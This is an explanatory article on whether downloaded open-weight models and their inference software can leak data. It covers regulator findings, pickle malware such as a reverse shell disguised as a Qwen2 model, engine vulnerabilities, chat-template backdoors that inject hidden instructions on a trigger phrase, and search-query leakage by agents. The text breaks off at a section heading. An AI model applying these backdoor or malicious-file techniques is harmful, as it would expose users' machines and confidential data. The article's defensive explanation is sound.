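# Can downloaded open-weight AI models send data back to their developer or a state, and can such behaviour be removed?

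## What is an open-weight model, and where does the data go when someone uses one?

An open-weight model is a language model whose developer publishes its weights, the numbers it learned in training, so that anyone can download them and run the model on their own machines. Examples include Meta's Llama, OpenAI's gpt-oss, the models of the French company Mistral, and the Chinese models DeepSeek, Qwen (from Alibaba), Kimi (from Moonshot AI) and GLM (from Z.ai). Closed models such as Anthropic's Claude stay under their provider's control, and customers use them through an account. "Open-weight" is a weaker label than "open-source". Few developers release their training data and code along with the weights, as Meinhardt, Nong and colleagues noted in *Beyond DeepSeek* (2025), so a person who downloads a model usually has no record of what went into its training.

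Since 2025 the strongest open-weight models have mostly come from Chinese laboratories, and their spread has raised a worry about espionage, since an installed model might send a company's data to the developer or the Chinese state. Models from any country have the same parts, and whether data leaves the company depends on which part handles it and whose machine that part runs on.

### The parts of the system

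The download consists mostly of large tables of numbers. Kimi K3, which Moonshot released in July 2026, has 2.8 trillion numbers. At four bits (half a byte) each, a common level of compression, they take up 1.4 terabytes.

The numbers do nothing until a program loads them. That program is the inference engine (llama.cpp and vLLM are two common ones), and its job is arithmetic. Text enters the arithmetic as tokens, which are words or fragments of words, each with its own number in a fixed vocabulary. Given the tokens so far, $x_1, \dots, x_t$, the engine uses the weights to compute a score $z_i$ for every token $i$ in the vocabulary, and then turns the scores into probabilities for the next token:

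$$P(x_{t+1} = i \mid x_1, \dots, x_t) = \frac{e^{z_i}}{\sum_j e^{z_j}}$$

The engine picks a token according to these probabilities, adds it to the text and repeats the computation until it picks a token that marks the end of the answer. Anything a developer has trained into the weights can affect the output only by changing how likely each token is.

A model that continues text also needs markers showing who is speaking. The chat template, a short set of formatting rules normally shipped with the weights, adds these markers around each turn of the conversation and puts the operator's standing instructions at the start.

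A program called the harness connects the engine to everything else. In a plain chat application, the harness shows the answer and keeps the history. In an agent, such as a coding assistant, it also carries out tool calls, which are actions the model requests in its output. The engine and the harness often come from someone other than the model's developer.

### One prompt, three routes

Take a lawyer who pastes a client's contract into a chat window and asks a DeepSeek model for a summary.

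If the window belongs to DeepSeek's own app, the phone sends the contract to DeepSeek's servers, where the company's engine computes the summary. Encryption can hide the text from the networks in between, although Krebs on Security (2025) reported expert warnings that the early mobile apps sent some user and device data unencrypted. The server has to work on the plain text, so DeepSeek can read the contract, as can any contractor it shares the text with and any authority with power over either of them. Intruders may also be able to read it. Christakis recounts in *DeepSeek and the China data question* that in January 2025 the security firm Wiz found a DeepSeek database open to the public internet, with over a million lines of chat histories and access keys.

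A product with another company's logo may still forward each prompt to DeepSeek's paid programming interface, in which case DeepSeek's servers process it. DeepSeek excludes such products from its privacy policy and leaves it to their makers to tell users what happens to the data.

The second route exists because the weights are public, so any company with enough hardware can run the model and rent out access to it. *The best AI you can own is Chinese* (Ferrari, 2026) reports that Microsoft told Axios in June 2026 it was evaluating a version of DeepSeek V4 on its own Azure cloud as a cheaper engine for its Copilot Cowork agent. Under that arrangement, anything the user submits, such as a contract, goes to the host, which can read it. DeepSeek takes no part in the computation and receives nothing unless the host passes something on. The host may well have dealings with the developer. *Open-Weight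 Diplomacy* (Sharma, 2026) reports that Moonshot's licence for Kimi K3 requires large hosting businesses to negotiate a separate agreement. Such an agreement covers the right to sell the model's output and does not by itself give Moonshot a copy of anyone's prompts.

The third route is self-hosting, where the lawyer's firm runs the weights on hardware that it controls. The contract travels from the lawyer's computer to the firm's server and back, and only the firm's administrators, or someone who breaks in, can read it. Christakis concludes that this removes the flow of data to China, the exposure to Chinese disclosure law and the reliance on DeepSeek's security practices. Ferrari makes the broader claim that open models on the user's own hardware "do not send anything anywhere". This is true of the arithmetic described above but not necessarily of the whole installation, because the engine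 and the harness are ordinary programs that can open network connections.

The cost of hardware also limits who self-hosts. The laptops that Microsoft and Nvidia announced in May 2026 can run models of roughly 120 billion parameters, according to Ferrari, but the Chinese flagships are many times larger. People who run "DeepSeek" on a laptop are running a smaller related model, often one trained on the flagship's outputs (a method called distillation) and then compressed. Anyone who wants to use the flagship itself needs a server room or a hosting provider.

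### Why the alarm began with DeepSeek's app

In January 2025, DeepSeek published the weights of its R1 model under a permissive licence and also offered the model as a free chatbot through an app and a website. Within days the app was at the top of the US iPhone store. The weights and the chatbot shared a name, but the regulators who then took action against "DeepSeek" were acting against the chatbot.

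The current version of DeepSeek's *Privacy Policy* (2026), dated 10 February, which covers the chatbot, states that the company will "directly collect, process and store" personal data in China. The data include user input, IP addresses, device identifiers and cookies. DeepSeek uses them to run the service and train its models, shares them with service providers and other companies in its group, and reserves the right to share them with law enforcement and public authorities. Accounts differ on whether the policy disclosed storage in China from the start. Christakis describes the December 2024 version as not saying where data was stored, but an Associated Press report in Fortune (2025) found the disclosure in the policy in early February 2025, and the Italian regulator had cited the policy for the same fact a few days earlier.

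That regulator, the Garante, was the first to act. On 28 January 2025 it asked two DeepSeek companies what data they collected and where they kept it. They answered the next day that they had not entered the Italian market, that they had removed the app from Italian stores and that EU data protection law did not apply to them. The Garante found that people who had already registered could still use the chatbot through the website. Its order, the *Provvedimento del 30 gennaio 2025* (2025), found that the companies had failed to cooperate, to inform users properly, to name a representative in the EU and to protect data that they stored in China. It prohibited them from processing the personal data of people in Italy "in the context of the DeepSeek service", which it defined as the app, the website, software and related services. The ban was still in force a year later, according to *DeepSeek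 One Year Later* (Christakis and Raj, 2026). It covers only processing by those two companies, so it doesn't apply to a firm in Milan that runs the R1 weights on its own server and does its own processing.

South Korea's Personal Information Protection Commission produced the most detailed account of where the data went. It found that between 15 January and 15 February 2025, DeepSeek sent Korean users' data to three companies in China and one in the United States without asking for consent or disclosing the practice. Volcano, a Chinese cloud company affiliated with TikTok's owner ByteDance, received the text of users' prompts along with device and network details. DeepSeek said it used Volcano's services to fix security weaknesses and improve the user experience. The commission judged the transfer of prompts unnecessary, confirmed that DeepSeek had blocked it from 10 April, and recommended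 that DeepSeek delete what it had already sent. Radio Free Asia's *China's DeepSeek transferred South Korean user info overseas* (2025) gives the commission's estimate that the transfers may have affected around 1.5 million users. That figure looks like 50,000 daily users multiplied by thirty days, which would count each daily user thirty times, so the true number of people is probably much lower. DeepSeek accepted the recommendations, and downloads resumed on 28 April.

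While the commission was still investigating the flow of prompts to ByteDance's cloud, its chairman, Ko Hak-soo, told reporters that companies' use of open-source models was "fundamentally something to be encouraged", but that agencies should watch for security problems, Asia Business Daily reported.

In Germany the case went to a state authority, the Berlin Commissioner for Data Protection (2025), Meike Kamp. Her office found that the DeepSeek app transfers everything users type or upload, together with location and device data, to processors and servers in China, and that DeepSeek had not shown that the data is protected to a standard equivalent to the EU's. On 6 May 2025 it asked the company to withdraw the app, stop the transfers or make them lawful. When DeepSeek did none of these, Kamp reported the app to Apple and Google on 27 June as illegal content. Both declined to remove it. Christakis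 thinks Berlin relied on the wrong article of the law, since the rules on "transfers" do not cover a foreign company that collects data directly from users, though other duties in the same law do. Nobody disputes that the app sends data from users' phones to servers in China.

Security researchers found heavily disguised code in the DeepSeek chatbot's web login page that, Fortune reported, "could send some user login information" to China Mobile, a state-owned telecommunications company. In April 2025, a US House committee asserted that DeepSeek channels American users' data directly to the Chinese Communist Party through infrastructure connected to China Mobile, according to Radio Free Asia. Code that could send login details is much weaker evidence than an observed transfer of data to the Party. The code is also part of DeepSeek's website, and running the weights doesn't require the website.

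### What a state can demand, and from whom

One of Kamp's reasons was that Chinese authorities have "extensive access rights" to personal data that Chinese companies hold. The best-known basis for this access is the National Intelligence Law of 2017, which obliges organisations and citizens to support, assist and cooperate with state intelligence work. The Cybersecurity Law also requires network operators to give technical support to the police and state security agencies. Kamp's office also found that DeepSeek's users do not have in China the enforceable rights or effective remedies that EU law guarantees. Outsiders cannot check how often the authorities use these powers on AI companies, and Christakis notes that DeepSeek has offered no transparency about it.

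Other states can also reach data on a company's servers. Under the CLOUD Act of 2018, a US provider that receives a valid warrant must produce data it controls, even if the data is stored abroad. An EU regulation of 2023 lets a judicial authority in one member state order a provider in another to hand over electronic evidence. Private parties can also obtain hosted conversations. In January 2026 a federal judge in New York ordered OpenAI to give twenty million de-identified ChatGPT conversations to news organisations that were suing it over copyright. Ferrari observes that OpenAI could comply because the conversations were on its servers. The safeguards in these systems differ greatly from China's, and for many users that difference is what matters most. But all of these powers depend on the company having the data or being able to get it.

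DeepSeek can't hand over a contract it never received. If a Chinese intelligence service ordered the company to collect what foreign law firms type into their self-hosted copies, the order would bind DeepSeek but wouldn't connect it to those firms' machines. To obey, DeepSeek would need something in the downloaded files, the engine or harness, or the model's trained behaviour to transmit the data, and a network that let the data out. The state could compel the company to try to build such a mechanism into its next release, which is the serious version of the worry, but the company couldn't add it to copies people have already downloaded. As Sharma points out, a downloaded weight file can be copied, run on the owner's machines and kept forever, and the vendor loses control of it once it is released.

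### How many people use Chinese models, and how many know it

Nobody has a full count of copies because no central register records those on private servers. Meinhardt and colleagues therefore rely on indirect signs, chiefly activity on Hugging Face, the main public site for sharing models. Chinese developers accounted for 17.1% of downloads there between August 2024 and August 2025, and American developers for 15.8%. In September 2025, Qwen overtook Llama as the most downloaded family of language models, and 63% of the new fine-tuned or otherwise derived models on the site were built on Chinese ones. These are rough measures, because an automated system can download the same file many times and a whole company can use a single download.

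The evidence for 2026 shows more about Chinese models' standing than about how widely they are used. Ferrari reports that in mid-July Kimi K3 ranked fourth among all models on one widely used index, and GLM-5.2 led the open models whose weights were already out. Microsoft's Foundry Local, a tool for building models into applications, lists Qwen and DeepSeek variants in its catalogue. Governments have adopted Chinese models too. Southeast Asia's flagship regional models use a mix of American and Chinese base models, which Sharma interprets as a deliberate hedge against dependence on either country.

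The much larger figures in circulation often describe use of DeepSeek's hosted service rather than its downloaded weights. Christakis and Raj cite a 960% rise in DeepSeek downloads in the nine months after R1, and Microsoft research that gives DeepSeek 89% of the market in China, 56% in Belarus and 43% in Russia. They use these numbers to measure how far the regulators slowed the hosted service. People who use that service send their prompts to China, so they should be counted separately from people who use the weights.

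Some people use a Chinese model without having chosen one. In March 2026 Cursor, an American company that makes a popular AI code editor, launched a coding model called Composer 2. After users spotted references to Kimi and pressed for an explanation, Cursor confirmed that it had built Composer 2 on Kimi K2.5, from the Chinese company Moonshot. Cursor vice president Lee Robinson said that only about a quarter of the computing behind the final model came from the base and the rest from Cursor's own training, according to eWeek's *Cursor AI Admits Composer 2 Was Built on Moonshot's Kimi Tech* (2026). *Cursor Fits Its Model to Its Agent* reports that the successor, Composer 2.5, has the same base.

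Moonshot said in a statement, which Willison (2026) reproduced, that Cursor accesses Kimi K2.5 through the hosting platform of Fireworks AI, another American company. This is the second of the lawyer's routes. When a programmer types proprietary code into Composer 2, the code goes to Cursor and its host, while Moonshot's role was to supply the weights that Cursor started from. Composer 2 may still behave in ways it inherited from Moonshot's model, to the extent that Cursor's further training left that behaviour in place.

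A model's origins can be harder still to trace. Thinking Machines Lab, an American company, released an open-weight model called Inkling in July 2026 and disclosed that some of its training drew on Kimi K2.5. Ferrari treats this as part of a longer chain, in which Chinese laboratories distil American closed models and Western developers of open models then learn from the Chinese ones. By the time a model reaches a laptop, one company may have distilled it, another compressed it and a third fine-tuned it, and no one keeps track of the steps.

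## Can the downloaded files, or the program that runs them, contact anyone?

The weights cannot contact anyone. To send data, a program must have the operating system open a connection to an address, and the arithmetic that produces a model's answer does not do this. But a download often includes other files, and the software that runs the model does more than this arithmetic. Whether data can be sent therefore depends on the file format, any code that comes with the model, and the settings of a few common programs.

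### Why the weights are inert

Inside the engine, each token becomes a list of numbers, its activations, which passes through a stack of layers. Layer $\ell$ takes the activations $h_\ell$ and computes

$$h_{\ell+1} = h_\ell + f(h_\ell; W_\ell)$$

where $W_\ell$ is that layer's share of the weights and $f$ is a fixed recipe of multiplications, additions and a few simple functions, which also mixes in information from earlier tokens. After the last layer, one more multiplication gives the scores for the next token. The engine's programmers wrote the recipe, and the weights only supply numbers for it. A developer can choose any values for $W_\ell$, and the engine will multiply by them, but no choice of values adds a step that contacts Beijing or San Francisco.

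This holds for a model from any country. OpenAI tells users of gpt-oss that it does not receive what they send to a self-hosted copy unless they share it or use one of its managed hosting partners. The same reasoning applies to DeepSeek and Qwen.

A model's weights can contain hidden malware, but they can't run it. *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates* (Fogel, Cohen and colleagues, 2026) cites earlier work in which researchers stored malware in the least significant bits of a model's weights and the model still worked. The engine only multiplies by those bits, as it does with the rest of the weights, so the malware can do harm only if a second program on the machine extracts and runs it. For an attacker who already has such a program in place, the weights are mainly somewhere to hide the malware.

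The argument assumes that the file contains only numbers, that the engine reads them correctly and that the engine has no other reason to use the network. It covers only the step from tokens to probabilities, not what happens to the resulting text. A model can write a web address or a command, and a developer might train it to do so in response to a trigger, but this sends no data unless a harness or a person acts on the text.

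### Files that run code when they load

Python, the language most AI software is written in, has a built-in format called pickle for saving objects to disk. A pickle file is a list of instructions for rebuilding the saved object, which Python carries out when it loads the file. The instructions can import a function by name and call it with arguments stored in the file. In a harmless model file, these functions rebuild tables of numbers. An attacker can instead name a function that runs operating-system commands, which Python will call as soon as the victim loads the model, before anyone types a prompt.

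Two newer formats, safetensors and GGUF, contain no such instructions. They hold tables of numbers with descriptions attached, and the loading program copies the numbers into memory.

*DITTO* (Qin, Li and colleagues, 2026) found pickle files in 929, or 9.3%, of 10,023 Hugging Face repositories that dated from July 2025 to June 2026 and had more than 1,000 downloads a month. OpenAI, NVIDIA and IBM were among the publishers. *PickleFuzzer* (2026) cites an older estimate that 80% of open models used pickle in 2023, and a count of 2.1 billion monthly downloads from pickle repositories by March 2025. The download count probably overstates the exposure, because many repositories keep an old pickle file beside a safetensors copy, and many people who downloaded from them may never have loaded the pickle file. *PickleBall* (2025) puts downloads from these mixed repositories at 1.70 billion a month.

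In March 2026 someone uploaded a pickle-based file to Hugging Face that posed as a Qwen2 model. Loading it opened a reverse shell, a connection from the victim's machine to the attacker's that lets the attacker run commands on the victim's machine. Three days later, the researcher halaali198 reported in *Reverse Shell Malware Disguised as Qwen2 Model on Hugging Face* that every scanner on the site had missed it. The attacker had packed the instructions in an archive format that the scanners could not read but that PyTorch, a standard library for running models, can open. The file has since been removed. The report describes an impostor using the Qwen name, not a release from Alibaba.

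Security firms had reported earlier cases of the same kind. JFrog described one in early 2024 in *Data Scientists Targeted by Malicious Hugging Face ML Models with Silent Backdoor*. ReversingLabs found two more in February 2025, and Hugging Face removed them within 24 hours, according to CNCF's *nullifAI*.

One defence is a loader that refuses dangerous instructions. PyTorch has a "weights only" mode that does this, but a flaw in it let a malicious file run commands. Version 2.6.0 fixed the flaw, according to an April 2025 entry from Spain's cybersecurity institute (INCIBE, *CVE-2025-32434*, 2025). Strict loaders also reject some harmless models. Qin and colleagues report that one failed to load 51 of 252 in its own evaluation.

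Scanners, which inspect a file before anyone loads it, can raise many false alarms. PickleScan, the tool Hugging Face uses, wrongly flagged 177 of 706 harmless files in Qin and colleagues' tests, and users will probably start to ignore that many warnings. The team's own scanner, DITTO, checks how a file uses each function it imports as well as the function's name. It caught all 92 malicious samples in their benchmark and flagged 0.7% of the harmless ones. Where a model also comes in safetensors or GGUF, it is simpler to use that version instead of the pickle file.

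### Code that the user agrees to run

Some new models have a design that Transformers, Hugging Face's standard loading library, does not yet support. Their developers put Python files that describe the design in the repository, and the library runs these files only if the user turns on an option called `trust_remote_code`. The code then has the same access to the machine, including its files and network, as any other program the user starts. Storing the weights in the safetensors format does not protect against this code.

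*An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (Siddiq, Romel and colleagues, 2026) uses DeepSeek-R1 to illustrate how loading a model can run code from its repository. The DeepSeek-R1 repository includes a Python configuration file, which can run on the user's machine when the user loads the model with the option to run custom code turned on. The paper reports nothing malicious in the file. Still, when custom code runs, the developer has provided some of the code running on the user's machine, which makes this case an exception to a common reassurance. A contributor to the Privacy Guides Community's *Local AI question* (2026) argued that open-weight developers can't collect data from local users because they don't provide the code that passes data to and from the model.

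Siddiq and colleagues found such code in 36,697 of the 2.1 million repositories on Hugging Face (1.74%) and in 4.65% of those on ModelScope, a Chinese model-sharing site. They scanned the repositories on five platforms with several code analysers and a tool that matches known malware signatures. The analysers found a lot of careless programming. The malware tool matched 7% of the Hugging Face repositories, but more than four-fifths of those matches came from a signature for a 3D graphics format, and the researchers did not regard the results as clear evidence of malware. This is only mildly reassuring, because a signature tool checks for known patterns and could easily miss new code that sends data to an unfamiliar address.

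Custom code also weakens the point that a developer cannot alter an already downloaded copy. According to Hugging Face's *Environment variables*, the download library checks the site for a newer version of a file even when the latest one is already on disk. If a user has trusted a repository's code and has not tied the installation to one version, a change the developer publishes could run on the user's machine the next time the model loads.

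Users can protect themselves by pinning the version after someone has read the code, or by waiting until an engine supports the model's design without custom code. They can't rely on the platforms for this, because none of the five that Siddiq and colleagues studied runs custom code in a full sandbox. In the forum posts the study collected, many developers thought the option only allowed the library to read a model's metadata.

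### Chat templates

The chat template, which adds the markers around each turn of a conversation, is a small program, though it looks like a settings file. Most templates are written in a language called Jinja2, which can repeat steps, test conditions and rearrange text, and the engine runs the template for every request. A GGUF file normally includes its template, so it can deliver a program even though the format has no loading instructions.

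The engine needs to run that program in a sandbox that confines it to handling text, and several engines have failed to do so. In llama-cpp-python, which lets Python programs use llama.cpp, a crafted template could run any code on the machine. OSV's *CVE-2024-34359* (2024) records the flaw in May 2024, and Safety's *PyPi* (2024) lists version 0.2.72 as the fix. vLLM's developers fixed a similar flaw in late 2025.

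The same mistake then turned up in SGLang, another inference engine. On 20 April 2026, CERT/CC, an American centre that coordinates the disclosure of software flaws, warned that a malicious model could run code on the server and steal data from it. SGLang's maintainers had not responded to the centre before it published the warning. Wiz's *CVE-2026-5760* lists versions before 0.5.11 as vulnerable. The recommended fix, quoted in The Hacker News (2026), is to switch to Jinja2's sandboxed mode. Three separate projects made this mistake, perhaps because a template looks so much like configuration that programmers forget it is code.

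A sandboxed template can't open a connection, but it can change what the model reads. Fogel and colleagues modified templates so that a chosen phrase in the user's message would add a hidden instruction to the prompt. They tested eighteen models on four engines. When the phrase was present, factual accuracy fell from 90% to 15% on average, and the models put an attacker's web address into their answers more than 80% of the time. The researchers measured no loss of quality when the phrase was absent. The modified files passed all of Hugging Face's automated scans. The attack doesn't send data by itself, because the address is only text in an answer, but it gives an attacker influence over any harness that acts on the answer.

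The person best placed to tamper with a template may have no connection to the model's developer. Developers usually release full-size weights, which volunteers then compress into the GGUF files that people run on their own computers. In April 2026 Hugging Face had roughly 180,000 repositories of GGUF files but only 3,130 distinct templates, so it is practical to check a file's template against the developer's original.

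### Bugs in the programs that read the files

A file that contains only data can still cause harm if the program reading it has a bug. When llama.cpp opens a GGUF file, it calculates how much memory the contents need and reserves that amount. NVD's *CVE-2026-27940 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, describes a flaw in this step. A crafted file could push the total past the largest number the program could store, which made it wrap round to a small number. The program then reserved too little memory and wrote at least 528 bytes of the attacker's data past the end of it. This type of bug can crash a program, and a skilled attacker can sometimes use it to run code.

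The flaw became public on 12 March 2026, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-27940* (2026), and llama.cpp's build b8146 fixes it. The project had fixed a similar bug in the same file in 2025 but missed some areas. In May 2026, *Security Advisory* (2026), posted to the oss-security mailing list, reported several more flaws in llama.cpp's GGUF readers and rated one critical.

Ollama, a popular program for running models locally, had a bug that could leak data. *Bleeding Llama* describes the bug, which the security firm Cyera disclosed in early 2026. An outsider without a password could use a crafted GGUF file to make an Ollama server read beyond the memory it should have used. A server's memory can include recent prompts. Roughly 300,000 servers on the open internet were potentially vulnerable until their owners installed version 0.17.1. By default, Ollama accepts connections only from the machine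 it runs on, but many of these owners had changed that setting. The data would have gone to the attacker, who need not have had any connection to the model on the server.

A model developer could in theory exploit a bug like these by publishing a malformed official file. This would be a clumsy way to spy, because the file would work only against certain versions of certain engines and would remain public as evidence that anyone could later examine.

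### What the common programs send by default

Most of the traffic that a self-hosting user sees will come from ordinary functions of the programs that run models. These programs check for updates and count their users, and some offer optional online features.

vLLM sends usage statistics unless the operator turns them off. The example in vLLM's *Usage Stats Collection* includes an identifier, the cloud provider, the processor and graphics card, the amount of memory, the general type of model and various engine settings. It contains no prompts or answers. Operators can read the collected data in a file on their own disk.

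Hugging Face's libraries also collect some data by default, and each library has its own policy. The fine-tuning library sends details such as the type of graphics card but not dataset names or file paths, according to the *TRL documentation*. The server program sends a signal every fifteen minutes when it runs in a Docker container, a common way of packaging software, according to *Collection of Usage Statistics*. The routine check for newer files probably reveals more than these statistics do. Each request must identify the file's repository, so Hugging Face can see that a machine at a certain internet address is loading, say, a DeepSeek model. If the user has logged in, the library also sends the user's access token by default.

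Ollama states that it does not see prompts or data when a model runs locally. Its March 2026 privacy policy allows it to collect the app's version, request counts, internet addresses and information about model downloads. LM Studio, a similar desktop app, sends its maker the terms people type when they search for models. When it checks for updates, it also sends the app's version, the operating system and the internet address, according to the policy that LM Studio (2026) last revised on 19 October. The app checks for updates whenever the user opens it, according to LM Studio's *Offline Operation*.

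The update check reveals very little, but the update that follows puts new code on the machine. Ollama downloads updates automatically on macOS and Windows and asks the user only to restart, so someone who has inspected one version is trusting the company again with the next.

Cloud models are the feature most likely to make a user send out a whole prompt by accident. Ollama introduced them in September 2025 for people whose computers are too small for the largest models. Ollama's *Cloud models* (2025) explains that they "behave like regular models", so they appear in the same list and start with the same command. One of the first was `qwen3-coder:480b-cloud`, where the suffix "cloud" means that the prompt is sent to Ollama's servers. A lawyer who overlooked the suffix and picked that entry for a client's contract would be using a hosted service while believing the model was local. Ollama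 requires an account for these models and says it does not train on the prompts. Its privacy policy lists "model inference providers" among the outside companies that may process data. LM Studio also has cloud models and web search, but only for users who buy them.

| Program | Who receives the default traffic | How to stop it |
|---|---|---|
| vLLM | The vLLM project | Set `VLLM_NO_USAGE_STATS=1` |
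| Hugging Face libraries | Hugging Face | Set `HF_HUB_DISABLE_TELEMETRY=1` to stop statistics, or `HF_HUB_OFFLINE=1` to stop all calls to the site |
| Ollama | Ollama Inc. | Set `OLLAMA_NO_CLOUD=1` to remove cloud models and web search; block the app's internet access to stop updates |
| LM Studio | Element Labs, the app's maker, and Hugging Face for model searches | Run it without a connection once the model is on disk |

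None of these recipients developed DeepSeek, Qwen, Kimi or GLM. But a developer does receive some data when a user installs its own app or downloads the weights from a site it runs. For example, Alibaba runs ModelScope and can see the internet address of anyone who downloads a Qwen model there.

### How to check

People who run a model locally can check whether it sends their data anywhere, because anything that leaves the machine has to cross their network. Users of a hosted service can't see what happens to their prompts on the company's servers.

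The quickest way to test whether a model runs locally is to download it, disconnect the machine from every network, restart the program and ask a question. If an answer comes back, the machine computed it from the files on its disk, because a cloud model cannot respond without a connection. The test does not rule out a program that saves text and sends it once the connection returns. Working offline is also a sensible way to open an unfamiliar file for the first time, because a reverse shell cannot connect to anyone from an isolated machine, although malicious code could still damage whatever is stored there.

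To find out what a connected machine sends, the user has to record its traffic with a packet-capture program such as Wireshark or in the logs of a router or firewall. The recording should begin before the program starts and cover loading the model, several prompts, a long idle period and a restart. Some connections have an obvious purpose, such as a call to Hugging Face or an update server, and the user can repeat the test with those features off. The `HF_DEBUG` setting makes Hugging Face's libraries log every request they send. If a very large model runs across several machines, heavy traffic among them is normal, and the connections to examine are those that leave the owner's network.

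Encryption hides the content of messages in a recording but leaves their destination and approximate size visible. Size is a weak clue, because a compressed summary of a contract is only a few kilobytes and could pass for a routine check. An organisation that wants to read the content can send the traffic through a proxy, an intermediate server that decrypts it, and install the proxy's certificate on the machine. Ollama's documentation explains how to run the program behind a proxy that uses its own certificate.

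A clean recording is evidence about only one version of the software over one period. It would miss code waiting for a date or phrase that had not yet occurred, and an automatic update could replace the tested version at any time. A firewall that blocks every address the owner has not approved gives continuing protection. Keeping the computer permanently offline is stronger still, but it rules out web search and any other tool that needs the internet.

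## What leaves the machine when a local model uses search, documents or other tools?

A language model can't search the web, open a file or send an email by itself, so the harness does these things for it. Some of the user's text may then leave the machine, even though the model is local.

### How a model uses a tool

Ollama's *Tool calling* gives an example with a Qwen model on the user's own machine. The user asks for the temperature in New York, and the harness and the model then go through four steps:

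1. The harness sends the engine the question along with a description of a tool. The description gives the tool's name, `get_temperature`, and the information it needs, which is the name of a city.
2. The model writes a tool call, which consists of the tool's name and the argument "New York" in a fixed format.
3. The harness recognises the format, runs the matching function and gets a result, 22°C.
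4. The harness adds the result to the conversation as text and sends the whole conversation back to the engine. The model then writes either an answer or another tool call.

The model only writes the text of the call. Nette's *Tool Calling (Function Calling)*, a manual for programmers, stresses that the application decides whether to run it. Some harnesses ask the user to approve each call, and others run every call automatically.

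In Ollama's example, the engine's address is `localhost`, the machine itself, so the conversation stays there. Only the third step can send anything out, and what it sends depends on the function. Furst's teaching example, *tool_demo.py*, gives a Llama model a function that adds two numbers, which sends nothing. A weather function must send the city's name to a weather service. An email tool sends whatever the model puts in the message. A tool that runs commands is the most open-ended, because a command can upload a file or contact any address the network allows.

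### How a confidential prompt becomes a search query

Suppose the lawyer's firm gives its self-hosted Qwen model a search tool, and the lawyer types this:

> Our client Halden Foods wants to drop its supplier, Brightwater Packaging, over the contaminated batch in March. Can it end the contract without notice?

The model might write a search call with the query `Halden Foods Brightwater Packaging contaminated batch end contract without notice`. Including the names is sensible because they help a search engine narrow its results, but the query also contains most of what the client would want to keep secret.

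If the firm uses Ollama's search service, the harness sends the query to ollama.com. According to Ollama's *Web search*, the request consists of the query, an optional limit on the number of results and a key from the user's Ollama account. It does not include the rest of the conversation. If the model then requests one of the results, the harness sends that page's address to Ollama, which returns the text.

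| Who | What they receive |
|---|---|
| The firm's own server | The full prompt, the search results and the answer |
| The search provider | The query, with both company names and the dispute; the account key; the firm's internet address; the time |
| A website the agent reads | A request for one page, which also shows the firm's internet address if the firm's own machine fetches the page |
| The firm's internet provider | The names of the sites contacted and the times, but not the encrypted query |
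| Alibaba, the model's developer | Nothing, unless it runs the search service or one of the websites |

The model could instead have searched for `terminate supply contract without notice contaminated goods`. The provider would then have learned only that someone at the firm was researching a common legal question. The lawyer may never see which query the model wrote, because many chat windows show only the answer or hide the searches behind a menu.

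People easily overlook that a web search has to leave the machine even when the model runs locally. For example, freeCodeCamp's *Build a Personal AI Web Research Agent with Ollama and Qwen* describes an agent that searches the internet and yet "runs entirely on my own machine to preserve privacy". Settings can also be misleading. OpenClaw, an agent harness, lets users search through a "local" Ollama installation without a key, but according to its *Ollama web search*, they must sign in to Ollama, and the results come from Ollama's web-search service. Running a search program on the firm's own server doesn't help much if that program forwards each query to public search engines. Searching a stored copy of a reference work keeps the query inside the firm.

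### Searching the user's own documents

A firm may have thousands of contracts, far more text than a model can take in at once. Retrieval finds the few passages relevant to a question and adds them to the prompt.

The harness first cuts the documents into passages. An embedding model, a small model trained for this purpose, turns each passage into a list of numbers, or vector, and gives passages on similar subjects similar vectors. An index stores the vectors. When a question arrives, the embedding model turns it into a vector $q$ as well, and the index compares it with the vector $d$ of each passage:

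$$\text{similarity}(q, d) = \frac{q \cdot d}{\lVert q \rVert \, \lVert d \rVert}$$

The harness copies the passages with the highest scores into the prompt, and the model answers from them.

If the embedding model, the index and the answering model all run on the firm's hardware, retrieval sends nothing out. This is practical because many embedding models are small enough to run on an ordinary laptop. But each part is also available as a hosted service, and a product advertised as using a local model may use hosted services for the other parts.

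| Hosted part | What its provider receives |
|---|---|
| Converting scans to text | Every scanned file |
| Embedding model | Every passage when the firm builds the index, and every later question |
| Index | The vectors, and usually the passages too |
| Answering model | The question and the passages that the index selected |

A hosted embedding model can expose far more than web search does, because it receives the whole archive, including documents that nobody asks about. Storing only the vectors with an outside company is safer than storing the text, but anyone who has the vectors and the same embedding model can guess a sentence, compute its vector and check whether it matches one in the index.

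### What outsiders can work out from an agent's searches

An agent that searches both private documents and the web may use what it finds in the documents to write its web queries. *MosaicLeaks* (Gurung, Gella and colleagues, 2026) measures how much this reveals, using 1,001 research tasks, most of which combine the two kinds of search. In its main example, an agent has to find out from internal documents how much the online traffic of a company called Lee's Market grew in 2020, then use the answer, 15%, to find a public web page. The agent searches the web twice for the company's traffic growth and then once for something else that involves the figure 15%. Each query looks harmless, but someone who sees all three can infer that the traffic grew by 15%.

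The researchers gave a second language model only the list of web queries and had it guess the private facts. With Qwen3-4B-Instruct as the agent, the second model got at least part of a private fact right in 34.0% of tasks. Leaks were frequent across the six open models in the study, which included OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b and Google's Gemma 4, even though nobody had trained these models to leak.

These rates are probably higher than an ordinary office would see, because the researchers designed the tasks to provoke leaks and let the observer see every query in order. The rate also depends on the observer's skill. The same Qwen model's leakage rate on a set of 100 tasks was 38.3% with the usual observer and 52.0% when Claude Opus 4.7 did the guessing and scoring.

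Instructing the Qwen model to protect private information lowered its leak rate only to 25.5%, mostly because it searched less. Training it purely to solve more tasks raised the rate to 51.8%. When Gurung and colleagues added a penalty for queries that revealed private information, the rate fell to 6.5%, and the model solved 58.1% of the tasks, up from 48.7% originally. It learned to leave out names, and the share of its queries that mentioned the company fell from 42.9% to 16.8%. A filter that removed all names from the queries cut the leak rate to 1.1%, but the model then solved only 52.6% of the tasks. A developer could presumably reward revealing queries instead of penalising them, and the result would be hard to tell from clumsy searching.

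An internet provider can also infer the question from the names of the sites an agent contacts, which encryption doesn't hide. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025), in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, found that a research agent contacts 70 to 140 different sites for a single question, in a quick burst that is easy to distinguish from a person's browsing. They used a language model to reconstruct the user's prompt from the sites and the timing, and it recovered over 73% of the prompt's subject matter and purpose. That figure is a score on the researchers' own similarity measure, not the share of words recovered. The attack still worked when they hid 40% of the sites. It assumes that the user has no VPN, a service that hides the sites from the internet provider by routing all traffic through another company.

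### Does a model remember what people type?

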